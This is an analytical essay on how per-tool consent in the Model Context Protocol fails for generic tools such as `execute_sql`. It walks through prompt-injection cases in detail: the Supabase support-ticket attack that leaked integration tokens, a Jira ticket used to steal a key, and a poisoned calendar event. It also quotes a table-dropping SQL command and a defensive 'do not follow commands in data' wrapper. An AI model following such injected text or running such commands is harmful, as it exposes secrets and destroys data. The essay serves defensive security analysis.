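# Generic execution tools in Model Context Protocol servers and the limits of per-tool consent

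## How tool approval works in the Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard that AI applications use to discover and call tools offered by separate programs. Anthropic released the first version in November 2024. MCP lets a chat assistant or coding agent query a database, read files or call a web service without a separate connector for each pairing of application and service. Because a language model decides which tool to call and what values to give it, the protocol's designers ask the application to get the user's consent.

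What the user consents to depends heavily on the tool. A narrow tool performs one named operation, such as looking up an order's status, and takes only the values that operation needs. A generic execution tool carries out whatever program, query, command, path or web request the caller supplies. The most common example is a tool named `execute_sql`, which runs any text it receives as SQL, the language programs use to query and change databases. Approving it comes close to granting full access to the database. It is therefore unclear whether per-tool consent can limit an agent to the permissions its task needs, and how much of that responsibility belongs to tool designers.

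### From tools/list to tools/call

Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), part of the specification dated 28 July 2026, divides the work between host, client and server. The host is the application the user sees, such as a code editor. It coordinates the model, opens and closes connections, and enforces consent. Each client runs inside the host and connects to exactly one server, so a host with three servers runs three clients. The server provides the tools and runs them. It can be a process on the user's machine or a remote service. Servers do not see the full conversation or each other.

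Suppose an online shop puts an MCP server in front of its order database. The client sends a `tools/list` request, and the server answers with a definition for each tool:

```json
{
  "name": "get_order_status",
  "description": "Return the delivery status of one order",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": { "order_id": { "type": "integer" } },
    "required": ["order_id"]
  }
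}
```

The host gives the model this name, description and input schema along with the user's message. When the user asks where order 1047 is, the model picks the tool and writes the arguments, here `{"order_id": 1047}`. The host may then pause and show the user the pending call. If the user agrees, or if the host does not ask, the client sends a `tools/call` request with the tool's name and arguments. The server checks the arguments, logs in to the database with an account its operator set up beforehand, runs its query and returns the result as text for the model to read.

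The host asks the user for consent, but the code that determines what the call will do is on the server. The host has only the tool's name, its description and the call's arguments. A `tools/call` request carries the name, the arguments and metadata such as the protocol version, but has no field to record that a person agreed. The server therefore cannot distinguish a call that the user read and approved from one that the host sent on its own. It also cannot refer to an earlier exchange on the same connection, because the July revision removed sessions from the protocol, as Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* records.

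### What the specification requires and what it recommends

In the Model Context Protocol specification, MUST marks an absolute requirement, and SHOULD marks a recommendation that an implementer may set aside for good reason. Nearly all the consent rules in its *Tools* chapter use SHOULD. There SHOULD always be a human who can deny a tool call. Applications SHOULD make clear which tools the model can use and SHOULD present confirmation prompts. Clients SHOULD show the user a tool's inputs before calling the server, to prevent malicious or accidental data leaks. The chapter also lets implementers choose any pattern of user interaction, and a host that runs every call silently can still conform.

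Under the specification, servers MUST validate all tool inputs, implement proper access controls, limit the rate of tool calls and sanitise outputs. Clients MUST treat tool annotations, the optional labels a server uses to describe a tool's behaviour, as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server.

Two of these duties, validation and "proper" access controls, do little for a generic tool. A server can validate an order number by rejecting anything that is not an integer, but the natural schema for `execute_sql` declares its query to be a string, so every SQL command passes. The chapter does not define "proper" access controls, so a server arguably has them even if it carefully checks each caller's identity and then runs any query under the most powerful account in the database.

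The previous version of the specification was blunter about consent. Its overview (Model Context Protocol, 2025) says hosts must obtain explicit consent before invoking any tool, though the "must" is in lower case. It also acknowledges that MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level", because the protocol governs messages between programs and the consent dialog is inside one of those programs.

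These rules have hardly changed. The first version of the tools chapter already recommended a human in the loop and required access controls, in the same words. The July revision redesigned much of the surrounding protocol. It also deprecated Roots, which let a server ask the client which folders to work in. The maintainers now suggest passing folders as tool parameters or in the server's configuration, which shifts more of the responsibility for limiting a tool's scope to the people who write and configure servers.

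### Installing a server, trusting a tool, approving a call

Users meet the word "allow" at several moments, and what they give away differs a good deal between them.

Users install a server before any tool call, and installing a local server means running someone else's program. Model Context Protocol's security guidance requires clients that offer one-click installation to show the exact, untruncated command, identify it as potentially dangerous, and let the user cancel. It also recommends warning users that the server will run with the same privileges as the client, and running the server in a sandbox, which restricts the files and networks it can access. Without a sandbox, a local server can do whatever the user's own applications can do, regardless of which tools it advertises. Anthropic accordingly tells users of its coding agent, Claude Code, to verify that they trust each server before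 connecting it.

With a remote server, the user typically grants an access token, whose scopes (named permissions such as `files:*` or `db:*`) limit the access it gives. The security guidance advises starting with a minimal set of scopes and requesting more when an operation first needs them, and it lists wildcard scopes as a common mistake. But if a server does not specify the scopes it needs, the guidance has clients request every scope the server supports, on the grounds that a general-purpose client cannot judge which ones matter. The guidance presents this as compatible with least privilege because the user and the authorisation server can still decline some of the permissions, though this relies heavily on a single consent screen.

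Standing approval is consent that covers a tool's later calls. *Permission modes*, from the data-warehouse company Snowflake, lists four ways to answer a prompt from the company's agent: allow this call, allow the tool for the session, always allow it, or reject. If the user chooses "always allow", the agent never prompts for that tool again on that machine, whatever arguments later calls contain. The affected tools include MCP tools and SQL execution. Some hosts have offered fewer options. In a forum post, *Per-chat session approval for MCP tools*, a user of the code editor Cursor complained that the only choices were to answer a prompt at every call, which could mean dozens of clicks in one chat, or to put the tool on an allowlist permanently.

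Per-call approval covers one `tools/call` request with the arguments shown on the screen. It is the only one of the three grants that ties consent to the arguments the model wrote. VS Code's *Manage approvals and permissions* tells users of Microsoft's code editor to review the tool's name and input parameters, then approve a single use or choose a broader approval. VS Code's *Use tools with agents* also describes editing the parameters of a call that awaits approval.

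Hosts let users switch easily between narrower and broader approvals. In VS Code, a user can trust all of an MCP server's tools with a single checkbox. Because a server's list of tools may change, this trust can extend to tools that did not exist when the user ticked the box, unless the host asks again. The "Allow all" permission level removes the prompts entirely, while "Assisted permissions" has a language model judge each call and prompts the user only about calls the model does not approve. An administrator or cautious user can also mark a tool as never eligible for automatic approval.

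### Reach, and a database with forty tables

The differences between these grants become clearer with a definition. Write *E(t, a)* for everything that tool *t* could read, change or send when someone calls it with arguments *a*. The reach of the tool is the union of these effects over all the arguments it accepts:

*reach(t) = ⋃ E(t, a), for every a that t accepts*

Approving one call grants *E(t, a)* for the arguments shown. Standing approval grants all of *reach(t)*, including calls the user has not anticipated. Installing a server grants whatever its process and credentials permit, which is at least the combined reach of its tools.

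In the shop example, the database has 40 tables, including orders, customers, payments and staff logins. The server connects with an account that owns the database schema and every table in it. This account can perform all four of SQL's basic row operations (select, insert, update, delete) on every table, which makes 160 combinations of table and operation. It can also alter or drop the tables themselves. Suppose two servers use this account and differ only in the one tool each offers. The first offers `get_order_status(order_id)`, which runs a fixed query that reads the status column of the orders table. The second offers `execute_sql(query)`, which passes its text straight to the database.

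| What the user grants | With `get_order_status(order_id)` | With `execute_sql(query)` |
|---|---|---|
| Approval of one call | The status of the one order shown | Whatever the query shown does, in any or all of the 40 tables |
| Standing approval | The status of every order, and no changes | All 160 combinations, plus altering or dropping any table |
| Installing the server | Whatever the server's code does with the owner account, in all 40 tables | The same |

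For the narrow tool, standing approval allows only a little more than approval of a single call. An agent could collect the status of every order by trying every order number, which a shop might object to, but it could not read a customer's address or change a row. The tool uses only one of the 160 combinations, and only one column within it. For `execute_sql`, the same click takes the user from approving one query they can see to approving everything the owner account can do.

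With `execute_sql`, even a single approved call can destroy or expose a lot of data. In the PostgreSQL database system, the four-word command `DROP SCHEMA shop CASCADE` deletes all forty tables. A subtler query might answer the question about order 1047 but also join the orders table to the customers table and return every column of both. The host would show the query accurately, but the user would have to know both SQL and the database to notice that it also fetches home addresses. Per-call approval of a generic tool therefore depends on how well the user understands the argument, which is a separate problem from people accepting prompts without reading them.

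Both servers hold the same owner password, so a malicious update or a programming error in the order-status server could still destroy the database. A narrow tool restrains the model and anyone who influences it, but not the server's own code. To restrain the code, the operator has to change the server's database account. If the new account can read only order numbers and statuses, the reach shown in the bottom row of the table shrinks for both tools. For `execute_sql`, the reach shown in the two rows above it shrinks as well, because no query can do more than its account allows. A designer can therefore reduce a tool's reach by having it accept fewer arguments or by giving the server weaker credentials.

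The principle of least privilege, which security engineers named in the 1970s, holds that every program and user should have only the permissions the job requires. A support agent that only reports deliveries needs to read one column of one table. Standing approval of `get_order_status` grants close to that, while standing approval of `execute_sql` under the owner account also grants access to thirty-nine other tables and permission to make any kind of change. The user may have clicked the same button to approve either tool.

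### Four hints and the question of trusting them

A host could in principle use tool annotations to determine how much caution a tool requires. The March 2025 revision of the specification introduced these annotations, which include four optional true-or-false hints about a tool's behaviour. The definitions below follow a draft of the Model Context Protocol schema.

| Hint | Meaning when true | Default |
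|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool does not modify its environment | false |
| `destructiveHint` | The tool may make destructive changes, beyond merely adding things | true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no additional effect | false |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool may interact with an open-ended set of outside entities, as a web search does | true |

The destructive and idempotent hints matter only for tools that are not read-only. All four hints default to the riskier value, so a client should assume that an unlabelled tool writes and destroys data, has a further effect each time it runs and reaches the outside world. None of the hints describes how much a tool reads or how sensitive the data is. According to Model Context Protocol's *Class ToolAnnotations*, in the documentation of the official C# library, read-only tools do not create, update or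 delete data in any system. Tools that return the current time and tools that return the whole customers table both meet that definition.

A label is part of the tool's definition and stays the same for every call, so an honest label must cover everything the tool can do. A server may set `readOnlyHint` to true only if no accepted argument leads to a change, and it must leave `destructiveHint` true if even one argument can destroy something. This works for `get_order_status`, since every call does the same kind of thing. But no label suits a tool that runs both `SELECT` and `DROP`. Labelling it destructive triggers a warning on every harmless lookup, and labelling it read-only misdescribes the calls for which a warning matters most.

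The `execute_sql` tool for BigQuery, Google's data warehouse, has one fixed set of labels for calls with very different effects. According to Google Cloud's *MCP Tools Reference*, it runs any query that BigQuery supports, and the examples range from inserting one row to dropping an entire dataset. The tool is labeled destructive, open-world, not read-only and not idempotent. These labels apply even when a caller uses the optional `dryRun` argument, which makes BigQuery check the query and estimate its cost without running it. The destructive label is therefore accurate for the tool but doesn't show whether a particular call could delete anything. Google partly addresses this with a second tool, `execute_sql_readonly`, and asks callers in the description to prefer it. With two tools, each can have labels that hold for all its calls, although the read-only tool may still read a great deal of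 data. Others have proposed labels that depend on the arguments.

A Model Context Protocol blog post, written almost a year after tool annotations were introduced, recounts the debate over whether clients could rely on them. Justin Spahr-Summers, a co-creator of the protocol, thought the information would be very useful if true, but asked what a client could do with a flag it cannot trust. Basil Hosmer went further and argued that clients should ignore all annotations from untrusted servers, even the display title. The maintainers compromised by making every annotation a hint that clients must distrust by default. Each client decides how much weight to give a hint based on the information it has about the server.

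Hosmer's position is hard to fault when a stranger wrote the server. A hostile server can declare itself read-only and delete files anyway, and a client that skips its prompt because of the hint lets the attacker decide whether the call needs approval. The case for hints rests on servers that the client has independent reason to trust, such as those a company runs for its own staff. With these servers, a client can approve reads automatically and prompt only for changes, which the blog post describes as the most common use of annotations. A policy engine, a program that applies an organisation's rules to each call, can also combine the hints with other evidence.

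The compromise depends on clients distinguishing trusted servers from untrusted ones, but the maintainers write that in practice most clients trust any server that has been installed. If so, the MUST about annotations rarely applies, because clients only receive hints from installed servers. By agreeing to run a server, a user would also be leading the client to rely on its hints and skip some approval prompts. Google Cloud's account is more favourable. It says that most clients treat the hints as untrusted, but also that the hints can help decide when to prompt. The two accounts may describe the same behaviour, since a client can officially treat hints as untrusted and still use them.

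The same blog post reports that no MCP client showed annotations in its approval prompts or let users filter tools by them. The closest equivalent in production was a read-only mode in GitHub's server, which about 17% of users had switched on. Many servers shipped without any annotations. Five proposals for new annotations were open at the time, including labels for secret or sensitive data. The published charter of the Model Context Protocol's annotations group includes the question of whether the existing four are adequate.

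### What a gateway can see

To avoid relying only on the user's approval, organisations can place a gateway, a program that inspects and forwards traffic, between clients and servers. The July 2026 specification made this easier. The sample tool that illustrates the change, `execute_sql`, is a generic one that takes a region and a free-text query. Its description is "Execute SQL on Google Cloud Spanner" (Spanner is a database that Google operates across several regions).

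The server marks the region parameter with an extra property, `x-mcp-header`. When the model calls the tool with the region `us-west1`, the client copies that value into an HTTP header, `Mcp-Param-Region: us-west1`. HTTP headers are labelled lines that precede the body of a web request. Other headers carry the protocol method and the tool's name, while the query stays in the body. According to the original proposal, on Model Context Protocol's site, the purpose is to make routing easier. A load balancer choosing between a cluster in Oregon and one in Belgium previously had to parse the whole body to find the region.

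Security teams can also enforce rules about tool calls more easily. Körbächer (2026), in *A platform team's guide to MCP 7-28*, gives the example of a rule that allows each tenant at most ten `execute_sql` calls a minute and forbids test machines to use the tool in one European region. Before July, Körbächer writes, enforcing such a rule meant parsing message bodies at the network's edge, and in most cases teams never wrote it. Now a gateway can enforce it by matching a few headers. The server must reject a request whose headers and body do not match, so a client cannot evade the rule by putting one region in the header and another in the body. Körbächer adds that gateways should reject requests that use older protocol versions, under which nobody checks for a mismatch.

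A rule of this kind controls how often and where `execute_sql` runs, but not what the query does, since ten calls a minute may be ten lookups or ten dropped tables. The specification would also let a server mark the query for copying into a header, because it is an ordinary string. However, the specification warns against exposing sensitive values in headers, and the gateway would then have to interpret SQL. The shop's narrow tool avoids this problem because the name `get_order_status` describes nearly all of the call's effect, so a gateway can allow or block the operation by name.

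### Deputies and injected instructions

This matters more because the user's wishes are not the only thing that shapes the arguments. Two older ideas from computer security help explain why. The first is ambient authority, the permissions a process has simply because of the account it runs under, whatever request it is serving. The shop's server has ambient authority because it runs every query under its owner account, whether the query comes from a manager's request or a stranger's trick.

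The other idea comes from a story that Hardy, in *The Confused Deputy*, calls nearly true. Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, kept a compiler in a system directory. The compiler had permission to write in that directory because it recorded usage statistics there. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system let the compiler open the file because the compiler had permission, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records. The user had no permission to write to that file, but the compiler used its own permission on the user's behalf.

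A confused deputy is a program with legitimate permissions that is led to use them by someone who lacks them. Hardy considers having the compiler check file names but finds no good rule, because the billing file was not the only sensitive one and new files would keep appearing. Anyone who tries to make `execute_sql` safe by searching queries for forbidden words faces a similarly open-ended list. Hardy's remedy was the capability, a reference that both identifies a file and authorises its use. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file, so the compiler would not need to apply its own authority to a name the user typed. MCP tool arguments are like typed file names in that they identify something without authorising its use. The specification calls a server-issued identifier, such as a shopping-basket number, "a name, not a capability" and advises servers that authenticate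 their callers to check authorisation on every call. An order number should get the same check if the shop's customers, and not only its staff, can reach the tool.

Outsiders can steer an agent through prompt injection, which is text in material the agent reads that it wrongly follows as an instruction. A language model receives the user's request and the contents of a web page or email as one stream of text, and it cannot reliably tell which instructions came from the user. The Model Context Protocol maintainers' post cites a demonstration in which researchers planted instructions in the description of a Google Calendar event. An MCP calendar server delivered the text to the agent, which could then act on it using a local tool that executes code. The post identifies the code tool as the crucial link and adds that a single injected instruction could make any agent with unrestrained shell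 access leak data. It also cites the programmer Simon Willison's "lethal trifecta", the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate externally that makes such theft possible.

The maintainers acknowledge that annotations do not make a model resist injected text, and they recommend network controls or sandboxing where a guarantee is necessary. Per-call approval can stop an injected call if the user recognises it. Under standing approval, nobody reviews the calls, so an attacker who controls the arguments can do anything the tool allows. In the shop example, someone who hijacks an agent that has `get_order_status` can make it look up deliveries. If the user has instead clicked "always allow" on `execute_sql` to save time on the same lookups, the approval also covers the attacker's queries.

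## Supabase's raw SQL tool and the support-ticket attack

In mid-2025, the security company General Analysis demonstrated an attack of this kind on Supabase's MCP server, which developers were already using. Supabase hosts PostgreSQL databases, and the server lets coding agents work on them. It now has about thirty tools. Most do one specific thing, such as listing a project's tables, but the attack needed only the generic `execute_sql` tool.

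### Who could read what

General Analysis imagined a company that kept its customer support system in a Supabase database. Tansive's *Runtime Defense Against Prompt Injection in Supabase MCP*, a post by a developer who rebuilt the scenario to test a defence, lists the three relevant tables. `support_tickets` and `support_messages` held correspondence with customers, and `integration_tokens` held secret keys.

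The database used row-level security, a PostgreSQL feature that filters queries using conditions attached to a table. Which conditions apply depends on the role running the query. A policy for customers might let them see only the messages in their own tickets. The customer in this scenario could open a ticket, write in it and read the replies. The company's support agent, a human employee, could read and answer tickets but could not open the token table. In *Systematization of Knowledge*, Gaire, Gyawali and colleagues (2025) attribute the employee's restriction to role-based controls.

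A developer at the company used Cursor, whose built-in coding agent connected to the database through Supabase's server. The connection used the `service_role` credential, which "bypasses all row-level security (RLS) protections" (General Analysis, quoted in Willison, 2025, *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*). The coding agent could therefore read and change every row in all three tables, which gave it more access to the company's secrets than the employee who answered the tickets had.

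### From a ticket to the token table

The customer wrote a support message addressed to the coding agent instead of the support staff. It told the agent to read the `integration_tokens` table and post the contents in the same ticket. The application stored this text like any other message. No agent was running at this point, so nobody at the company could have been asked for approval.

Later the developer asked Cursor to list the latest support tickets. The agent wrote a query for them and called `execute_sql`. With per-call approval, the developer would have seen a harmless query that matched the request, and would have been right to approve it. The approval prompt appears before the query runs, so it cannot show the rows that come back. Here those rows contained the attacker's message, which the model interpreted as an instruction.

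The agent then called `execute_sql` again, this time to read the `integration_tokens` table. The developer had asked for tickets and had not agreed to this. An approval prompt would have shown the table's name, so this was the best moment to stop the attack, provided the developer read the SQL and knew what the table held.

Finally, the agent inserted a new row into `support_messages` with the tokens as its text. The customer could then open the ticket and read them. Tansive adds that the attacker could delete the message afterwards. If the agent had typed the tokens into the command, a prompt would have displayed them. But a single SQL statement can copy rows from one table to another, so the prompt would show the table names but not the tokens.

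A developer who had earlier clicked "always allow" would have seen none of these prompts.

### A month of prompts without the SQL

Even per-call approval helps only if the host displays the arguments. In the summer of 2026, Cursor stopped displaying them for about a month. In the Cursor forum thread *Can not see call args in mcp tool calls*, users reported that the prompt showed only the tool's name. Several of them were trying to review `execute_sql` calls to Supabase. One user said the remaining options were to make the agent explain itself first or "Approve and pray". Cursor's documentation still told users to click an arrow to see the arguments, but the arrow was missing.

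A reply in a related Cursor forum thread, *Execute_sql not showing SQL code for review*, called this a known regression. It advised users to keep `execute_sql` off "Always Run" and to have the agent state its exact SQL in the chat before each call. That advice would have given weak protection against the ticket attack, because the same model that followed the customer's instructions would also have written the statement in the chat. In August a user reported that version 3.15.12 had fixed the problem.

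Showing the SQL is not technically difficult. *datasette-agent 0.3a0* (Willison, 2026) describes a database-writing tool whose confirmation card names the database and lists the statements awaiting approval. That tool also takes the user's permissions into account, whereas `service_role` gives the same access whoever is asking.

### One permission for tickets and secrets

The developer had a good reason to let the agent read tickets and no reason to let it read tokens, but the connection offered no way to approve one without the other. The host handled both reads as calls to `execute_sql` with a string argument, and the database ran both as `SELECT` statements under `service_role`, which could read every table.

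Separation at either level would have stopped the theft. If the server had offered a narrow tool, `list_recent_tickets(limit)`, instead of raw SQL, the injected message would still have reached the model, but no value of `limit` would have let the model read the token table. A designer can cover a whole database this way by defining entities, such as tickets, and offering a fixed set of operations on each.

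Alternatively, the server could have kept `execute_sql` but connected with a weaker account. An account named `ticket_reader`, say, might hold a single grant on these tables:

```sql
GRANT SELECT ON support_tickets, support_messages TO ticket_reader;
```

PostgreSQL would then have rejected the query for tokens, even if the developer had approved it. Such narrow permissions are unusual. *MAP* (Ma, Dai and colleagues, 2026) found that 81.5% of 254 public database servers requested more authority than their code appeared to use.

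The coding agent was a confused deputy, like the compiler at Tymshare: the customer could not query the token table, but the agent could.

### Supabase's reply

Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025), published that September, accepted the central point that anyone who connects an AI agent to a live production database without further safeguards risks leaking data, whichever company hosts the database. The reply also disputed parts of the story.

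The reply said that no Supabase customer had reported a data leak through MCP. General Analysis had staged a demonstration, and neither the reply nor Willison's account points to a real victim. The lack of reports is only weak evidence that no leak happened, because a theft of this kind would reach the database as ordinary queries from an authorised account. It is better evidence that attackers were not already using the technique widely.

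Supabase also rejected the claim that MCP bypasses row-level security, which it said remained fully enforced. In the same passage, it conceded that an MCP server may run with higher privileges, as this one did. Both statements can be true because row-level policies apply only to some roles. In the demonstration, the policies still limited the customer to reading one ticket, but they did not restrict `service_role`, so the agent could copy the tokens into a row the customer was allowed to read.

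Supabase's broadest argument was that the weakness comes from how language models interact with tools and would appear with any API or database connection. General Analysis largely agreed. One of its co-founders wrote in a July discussion on Hacker News that the flaw was technically not Supabase's responsibility. The co-founder blamed unsanitised data in the agent's context, models that cannot tell instructions from data, and "bad access scoping", meaning that Cursor had too much access. Neither MCP nor Supabase can do much about how models read text, but the people who design a server can limit access through their choice of tools and credentials.

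Supabase had already tried to make the model more resistant by having its server wrap query results in an instruction not to follow commands found in the data. The engineers tested this on less capable models, which are more likely to follow injected instructions, and one engineer wrote on Hacker News that the published attacks had stopped working. The company also experimented with classifiers, models used to detect dangerous content. By September it had concluded that these measures "reduced risk but did not eliminate it".

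Critics on Hacker News had expected this. The commenter tptacek compared the wrapper to cleaning up a stranger's JavaScript and then running it with full trust, which tptacek said has never worked. Willison argued in the same thread that stopping 99% of attacks is a failing grade in application security, because an attacker can keep trying variations until one succeeds. No one can guarantee that a warning to a language model will stop every attack, whereas programmers can completely close an SQL injection hole once they find it.

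The reply's main advice was therefore to keep agents away from production data and give them development databases or anonymised copies. It also told users to leave manual approval on, be wary of "Always Approve" and log every query. It warned that people tire of approving calls and that part of a prompt's text may be off the screen. But, as the reply says, many people who build software with AI work alone, have no security team and develop directly on their production database. The advice matters most for these users, but they would have to set up a second environment before they could follow it.

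In its May 2026 documentation, Supabase repeated the advice never to connect the server to production data and used a support-ticket attack as its example of prompt injection. The company has since softened this advice. Snap's *Supabase MCP Server*, a newer copy of the documentation on Snap's cloud platform, permits a production connection when the task requires it and the server's restrictions are switched on, which makes those restrictions more important.

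### What the server's settings would have stopped

The demonstration had all three parts of Willison's "lethal trifecta": private data, untrusted text and a way to send data out. Most attacks of this type depend on a user combining several MCP servers, but Willison pointed out that Supabase's server supplied all three by itself. A useful setting has to remove at least one of them.

| Setting | What it does | Effect on the support-ticket attack |
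|---|---|---|
| Read-only mode | Runs `execute_sql` as a read-only PostgreSQL user and turns off the other tools that make changes | Blocks the write into the ticket; the agent can still read tickets and tokens |
| Project scoping | Limits the server to one project and removes the account-management tools | Blocks nothing, because the tickets and tokens share a project; protects the company's other projects |
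| Feature groups | Switch whole groups of tools on or off | Block nothing while the database group is on; with it off, the agent cannot query tickets either |
| Confirmation of destructive SQL | Asks the user to confirm when the server detects a destructive command | Probably blocks nothing, because the attack only reads and adds rows |

Users have to choose these restrictions. The sample configuration in Supabase's README uses the server's address without parameters, which leaves read-only mode off and gives access to every project in the account. In the README, Supabase recommends both read-only mode and project scoping, and says that addresses copied from its dashboard or documentation include the parameters.

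The database feature group contains both `execute_sql` and the much narrower `list_tables`, so a developer cannot use feature groups to keep one and drop the other. Removing unrelated groups still helps because it leaves a hijacked agent fewer tools to misuse. One default group, for instance, lets an agent deploy new code to Supabase's servers.

The newest of these controls is a confirmation step for destructive SQL. The server pauses the call and sends the user a form through the MCP client. Snap describes this step as a guardrail that may miss some destructive operations. It works only with clients that support these forms, and some clients can answer them automatically, so an accepted form does not prove that a person read it.

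Read-only mode is the only setting in the table that reliably breaks the demonstrated attack chain, because PostgreSQL enforces it regardless of what the model has read. But it doesn't restrict which database tables the agent can read, so an injected instruction can still make the agent fetch the tokens or every customer's personal details. The results enter the model's context and may appear in the chat. Supabase called prompt injection its "number one concern" even in this mode.

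Data in the model's context can also leave without a database write. In *When a Jira Ticket Can Steal Your Secrets*, Willison (2025) describes a demonstration by the security company Zenity Labs, again against Cursor. The attackers sent a support request that became a ticket in Jira, a program for tracking work. The ticket disguised a secret key as a "rotten apple", asked the agent to find it in the company's code, and then directed the agent to a web address that would carry the key out. A developer who combines read-only Supabase access with a tool that can open web pages therefore restores a way for data to leave, which read-only mode had removed.

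The problem is more pressing when users approve tools in advance. For unattended monitoring, where nobody can answer prompts, Snap advises users to pre-approve only the project-scoped, read-only tools the routine needs. If `execute_sql` is one of them, that approval covers every query that can read the project's data. The same documentation recommends using the narrowest query that can answer the question, but the model writes the query and so decides how narrow it is.

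Access tokens have improved since the demonstration. Supabase promised finer permissions in its reply and, in newer documentation, tells users to limit tokens for automated jobs to a single project and the permissions their tools need. But those permissions correspond to tools, so a token that allows `execute_sql` for ticket queries still allows it for queries that read secrets.

### Keeping tickets and SQL in separate contexts

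With all of these settings, the same model still has access to both the ticket text and the SQL tool. On Hacker News, tptacek objected to this arrangement and proposed splitting the work between two model contexts. The first reads tickets and produces structured data. Ordinary program code checks that data, including which tables it refers to, and discards anything unexpected. The second context, which never sees the tickets, turns what remains into SQL. Cursor offered no way to set this up, and tptacek considered it "insane" to connect Cursor to a production database.

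Another commenter, saurik, replied that instructions could still cross the barrier inside any field that holds free text. A customer might choose a username that reads as a command, and the checking code would pass it along as a name. The database is also full of customer-written text, so even if the second context never sees a ticket, a legitimate query may return a shipping address with instructions in its second line. In saurik's view, the check therefore belongs between the model that writes the SQL and the database that runs it.

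The two did not settle the matter, although tptacek suggested building such a system and letting people attack it. The point about stored text is hard to answer if the second context can run any SQL, because keeping tickets away from it blocks only one of the many ways malicious text can reach it. Separation is more convincing when each context also has less access. A third commenter, vidarh, proposed a strict rule that an agent should have no more permission than the least privileged person whose text it is processing. Under that rule, the coding agent could not have read anything the customer couldn't while it was reading the customer's ticket. The rule would also make many ordinary tasks awkward, since a developer investigating a fault often needs to look at several customers' records at once.

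Tansive tried a less drastic version that kept raw SQL. A script parses each query before it reaches Supabase's server and checks it against rules for the user's role. A support engineer can query only the two support tables. A DevOps engineer, who maintains the company's systems, can read the tokens but not the customers' messages, which keeps the tokens away from the text most likely to carry an attack. When the agent tried to fetch the tokens in a role without access to them, the script rejected the query.

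The post promotes its author's software, and it acknowledges that PostgreSQL roles could have enforced the limits in this example. saurik noted that a filter placed in front of a database may interpret a query differently than the database does. Roles would avoid this problem, because PostgreSQL would enforce a grant on two tables against the query it runs.

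## Database accounts behind 254 SQL servers

Restrictive grants protect a database only if someone sets them up. Ma and colleagues studied public SQL servers and found that the database privileges each server requests seldom match what its code does. They also built MAP, a system that limits a server from the outside when its account has too many privileges.

### What the servers ask for

The researchers started with 10,862 records of MCP servers from two public collections. They found 272 source-code repositories that work with relational SQL databases and retrieved 254 of them. The other 18 were private or no longer available.

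They sorted database privileges and operations into three classes, from least to most powerful.

| Class | Privileges an account may hold | Typical statements |
|---|---|---|
| READONLY | Reading data | `SELECT` |
| WRITE | Modifying data | `INSERT`, `UPDATE`, `DELETE` |
| ADMIN | Managing tables or roles, or unrestricted access | `CREATE`, `DROP`, `ALTER`, `TRUNCATE` |

The researchers assigned each repository two classes. They based the first on the privileges the server requests, as shown in its setup instructions, grant statements and connection settings. They based the second on what the server does, as shown in the SQL written into the code, the code that assembles queries and the calls to database drivers. They counted a server as over-provisioned if the first class was higher than the second.

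By this measure, 207 of the 254 servers (81.5%) requested more access than their code showed they needed. Forty-seven explicitly requested root (the administrator account in MySQL), superuser status or all privileges, and 31 of those had only `SELECT` and `INSERT` statements in their code. One server recommended a superuser account although its code only read three metadata tables.

Glama's *MCP Server for MySQL*, a page in an online directory of MCP servers, describes a server that disables all write operations by default, but its sample configuration logs in as `root`. A mistake in the server's own checks could therefore expose the whole database to changes.

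The researchers also found working credentials in the code of 46 repositories (18.1%), after excluding placeholders and non-working examples. These repositories contained 252 passwords and 83 complete connection strings. One server used a built-in root password if the user didn't set one. Anyone who can read such a repository and reach the database can log in without going through MCP or its approval prompts.

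### Where the 81.5% figure is too high, and where it is too low

The comparison leaves out queries that exist only at runtime, as Ma and colleagues acknowledge, and nearly all of a generic tool's queries are of this kind. Glama's *execute_sql* reproduces the code of one such tool, from another MySQL server. The code passes the caller's string to the database with `cursor.execute(query)`. The only SQL statement in the function is `SHOW TABLES`, which the code checks for so that it can format the result. Someone who searched this code for SQL would conclude that the server only reads, although the tool's description also lists inserts, updates and deletes.

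If the study scored generic tools this way, it counted too many servers as over-provisioned. A user who wants an agent to correct records through `execute_sql` needs an account with write access, which the study would have treated as excess.

The researchers could also have made the opposite error, by deciding that a bare `cursor.execute(query)` needs unrestricted access and putting the server's code in the ADMIN class. No account ranks above ADMIN, so they could not then have flagged that server, whatever account it used. But they left only 47 servers unflagged (the number requesting root is also 47, by coincidence). If more than 47 servers offer a generic tool, the researchers must have put some of them in a lower class and flagged them. The paper does not count generic tools, but it describes a typical database server as one that registers tools "such as query or execute_sql". The error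 in classifying generic tools therefore probably inflates the figure. It would have to be large to reverse the finding, since about 160 of the 207 flagged servers would have to offer a generic tool before the rate among the remaining servers fell to half.

The three classes are also too coarse to show much of the excess access. Suppose the online shop's `get_order_status` server used an account that could read all 40 tables. The study would record a match because the code and the account both read data, although the tool needs only one column of one table. It would also record a match if a server only added rows to a log but its account could delete every customer. The 81.5% figure may well understate the share of accounts with more access than the job requires.

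The figure also combines two different risks. If a server has only narrow tools, only its own code can use the account's extra privileges, whereas a generic tool lets the model use them too. A server with a generic tool that the study flagged by mistake may therefore be more dangerous than a server with narrow tools that it flagged correctly.

It is also unclear how many people use these servers. One of the two collections comes from *A Measurement Study of Model Context Protocol Ecosystem* (Guo, Hao and colleagues, 2025), which found that more than half of the projects listed in six online marketplaces were invalid or of little value. Of the 8,060 servers that passed its filter, 21.9% had not been updated for more than a year. Ma and colleagues could get only 123 of their 254 servers to run queries, because the others had incomplete code, missing dependencies or requirements the researchers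 could not meet. Their study counts an abandoned experiment and a widely used product equally, and it records the requests in the instructions, which a careful operator may ignore.

### A reporting server that dropped a table

To show what excess privileges allow, the researchers set up an analytics server meant to read data for reports, but gave its account administrative privileges. An ordinary reporting query worked as expected. Adversarial text in the agent's context then led the workflow to run `DROP TABLE`, an administrative operation, which deleted a table of user identifiers, names and email addresses. The audit log recorded the deletion as an administrative command from an authenticated account.

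The server had logged in to the database with a valid password, and every later query ran under that account. When the `DROP` statement arrived, the database checked whether the account had permission to delete the table, which it did. The connection carried no information about the server's job, the user's request or whether anyone had approved the tool call, so the database had no basis for rejecting the statement. If a reporting service and a maintenance service share an account, the database applies the same permissions to both, even though the same statement may be routine from one and disastrous from the other.

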